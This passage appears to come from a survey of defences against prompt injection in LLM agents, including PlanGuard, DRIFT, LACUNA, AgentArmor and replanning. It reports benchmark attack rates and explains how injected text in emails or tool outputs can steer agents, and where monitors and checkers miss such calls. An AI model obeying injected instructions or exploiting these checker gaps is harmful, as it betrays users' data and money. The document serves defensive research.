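The third case is common because models express the same thing in different ways. For example, the planner might write `last_week` and the agent `lastweek`. On InjecAgent, exact matching alone blocked 27% of harmless cases in one half of the benchmark and 38% in the other. Adding the model's judgement reduced these false alarms to about 1% and 3%.

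The attacks' success rate fell from 72.8% to 0%. Gong and Deng had instructed the unprotected agent to obey commands in tool outputs, so the 72.8% rate doesn't describe a normal agent. Exact matching also reduced the rate to 0% without the model, so the test gives little evidence that the model can recognise malicious arguments. The model's input includes the agent's reasoning, which hostile text may have influenced.

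PlanGuard restores less of an agent's freedom than its design suggests, because an agent that finds it needs a tool outside the plan still can't use it. InjecAgent's tasks have only one step, so testing on them doesn't show this limitation. Gong and Deng acknowledge another limitation, using the request "Pay the bill in the email" as an example. The plan includes a payment but not the correct account number, so the agent's choice of account can't be checked against it. The published procedure also keeps no record of earlier calls, so it would allow the same planned payment twice.

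DRIFT allows more departures from the plan. Its planner lists the expected calls in order, with a checklist of arguments for each. If the agent makes a call that isn't on the list, DRIFT allows it when the tool only reads data. When the tool changes data or contacts somebody, a language model checks whether the call fits the user's request. If it does, DRIFT adds the call to the plan. Otherwise, the user decides. Before the agent reads a tool's output, a separate model removes any instructions in it that conflict with the user's request.

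In DRIFT's own AgentDojo tests with GPT-4o-mini, these components had the following effects:

| Configuration | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Unrestricted agent | 63.6% | 30.7% |
| Fixed constraints | 43.2% | 2.1% |
| Constraints that can change | 58.5% | 5.4% |
| Changeable constraints and filtered outputs | 57.3% | 1.4% |

Letting the constraints change recovered about three quarters of the lost usefulness but more than doubled the rate of successful attacks. Adding filtering then brought that rate below the one for fixed constraints. This is a good tradeoff on these tests, but the protection depends on models that read outside text or judge an agent that has read it.

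In later tests, Ma and colleagues, who include some of DRIFT's developers, found that DRIFT lowered GPT-4o-mini's usefulness by 18 percentage points, compared with about 6 in the original experiment. They left out AgentDojo's workspace tasks, which may explain part of the difference. They also let another model revise the injections after seeing which ones worked, and the attack success rate against DRIFT rose from 2.6% to 6.4%.

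Allowing every read is also risky. Reading another page doesn't change the user's files, but it can expose the agent to more hostile text. A request to a web server can also include private data in the address. Whether DRIFT would allow such a request depends on whether its model classifies the tool as read-only.

### Checking code one piece at a time

*LACUNA* describes a system from the same EPFL group as TACIT that lets a program leave gaps for a model to fill during the run. Suppose a developer writes:

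```
val letter   = readFile("landlord.txt")
val deadline = agent[Date](s"When must I reply? $letter")
val reply    = agent[String]("Draft a reply before the deadline")
```

When the run reaches the second line, a model receives the letter and writes Scala code that must produce a date. The compiler checks this code as if the developer had written it there. If the code passes, it runs, and the model that fills the next gap can use the date. The generated code can contain further gaps, so a model can divide a task into smaller ones as it learns more.

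The compiler accepts or rejects each piece of the program as a whole. In one example, a model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new number. It writes code that would subtract the 50 but return a sentence, so the compiler rejects the code and the balance stays at 100. Ordinary Python would have subtracted the 50 before anything detected the mistake. However, rejecting one piece doesn't undo the earlier pieces that have already run.

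LACUNA doesn't isolate the model from hostile text, so if the landlord's letter contains an injection, the model may write the code the attacker wants. With capture checking on, that code can use only the capabilities available at that point in the program. The developer can give a gap access to files but not the network, and a hostile letter can't change that. If the gap has access to both, the letter may lead the model to write code that sends a file to somebody.

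The design also removes a limitation of TACIT's wrapper for secrets. In TACIT, the cloud model can't read a classified contract but has to write the function that processes it. LACUNA lets that function call a trusted local model, which reads the contract and writes code to suit it. The compiler still requires the new code to be pure, so the code can't send the contract anywhere.

On AgentDojo, agents completed more tasks with LACUNA than with TACIT in seven of eight comparisons, by roughly 2 to 7 percentage points. Eight of 1,898 attacks succeeded against LACUNA, compared with one each against TACIT and CaMeL. Seven of those eight were with Gemini 2.5 Pro. With o4-mini, at most one attack succeeded against each system. The small increase fits LACUNA's design, in which an injection can influence code that the model has not yet written.

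In simulated customer service, the flexibility didn't make up for the difficulty of writing typed code. DeepSeek-V4-Flash completed 76.0% of the τ²-bench tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. That is a substantial loss, although the paper calls the results "on par". The compiler rejected 22.4% of the model's code in the shop tasks, and 89% of the code from the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite in the telecom tasks.

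### Treating the run as a program

An agent that never writes a plan still leaves a record of what it has read and done. *AGENTARMOR* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) analyses this record as if it were a program. The system, built at ByteDance, updates a graph as the agent works and checks it before each tool call. The graph contains the prompts, the model's stated reasoning, and the tools with their arguments and outputs. Arrows show the order of the steps and which items influenced others.

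Suppose a user asks an agent to install a program, and the agent proposes to download a second one. AgentArmor should connect the download to the user's request if the user named both programs, or to the first program's instruction file if the idea came from there. It then combines these connections with information about the tools and data, gives each item a security label, and decides whether to allow the call.

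This lets the agent change direction freely, but AgentArmor, like any run-time monitor, can analyse only the steps taken so far and the next proposed call.

AgentArmor's graph is less reliable than one made from a program's source code. In code, an assignment shows exactly which values went into a result, but AgentArmor has to infer which text led a model to choose a call. If it wrongly connects a hostile call to the user's request, the call may pass the check. Even careful label rules can't correct for a missing arrow.

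On AgentDojo, AgentArmor reduced successful attacks to an average of 3%, while agents completed only about 1% fewer tasks. But few AgentDojo tasks require the agent to follow a harmless instruction from a third party, so the results don't show how well AgentArmor would distinguish a genuine login request from an attack.

### What replanning can keep

How much of the original guarantee remains after replanning depends on what the planner reads before it writes the new plan. If it reads only trusted data, as f-Secure's planner does, replanning preserves isolation completely, but the planner can't adapt the plan to the contents of an email from a stranger.

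A planner can also respond to untrusted content safely, to a degree, if it receives only answers from a short fixed list. For example, a quarantined model might answer only yes or no when asked whether a page requires a login. If an attacker controls three such answers and the planner has read nothing else from the attacker, the attacker can choose among at most eight continuations (2 × 2 × 2). Branch steering gives an attacker the same power over a plan with three yes-or-no branches. A checker can examine all eight continuations in advance.

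Once the planner has read the full untrusted text, the new plan and later plans from the same conversation are no longer isolated from that text. Checking can still limit the damage, as long as the checker treats the planner as possibly hostile and the planner can't change the rules. DRIFT weakens this protection because text the agent has read can lead to a call that a model then adds to the permitted list. LACUNA keeps the developer's limits fixed while the generated code changes.

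The checker also has to keep track of what happened under earlier plans. Otherwise a first plan could save a bank statement in an ordinary file and a second could email that file, and neither plan would break a rule on its own. SPA prevents this by storing labels with its results. Soteria, which writes a new plan after each customer message, can apply its rules to the log of earlier calls.

Even with this memory, an agent that replans can no longer be sure before it starts that the whole task is allowed. Like an agent with only a monitor, it might cancel one hotel and then find that the rules prevent it from booking another. If the task allows that order, the agent could postpone actions it can't undo until it has read everything it needs and a checker has approved the remaining steps.

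A request such as "Do what this email asks" remains difficult under any of these designs. The user has let the email's author choose the action, so a checker can't identify an attack merely by noticing that the action came from the email. Fixed rules can still forbid payments or deletions. For other consequential actions, the agent can read the email, propose a plan and ask the user to approve it. This gives the user concrete actions to judge, but it works only if approval requests are rare enough that people keep reading them.
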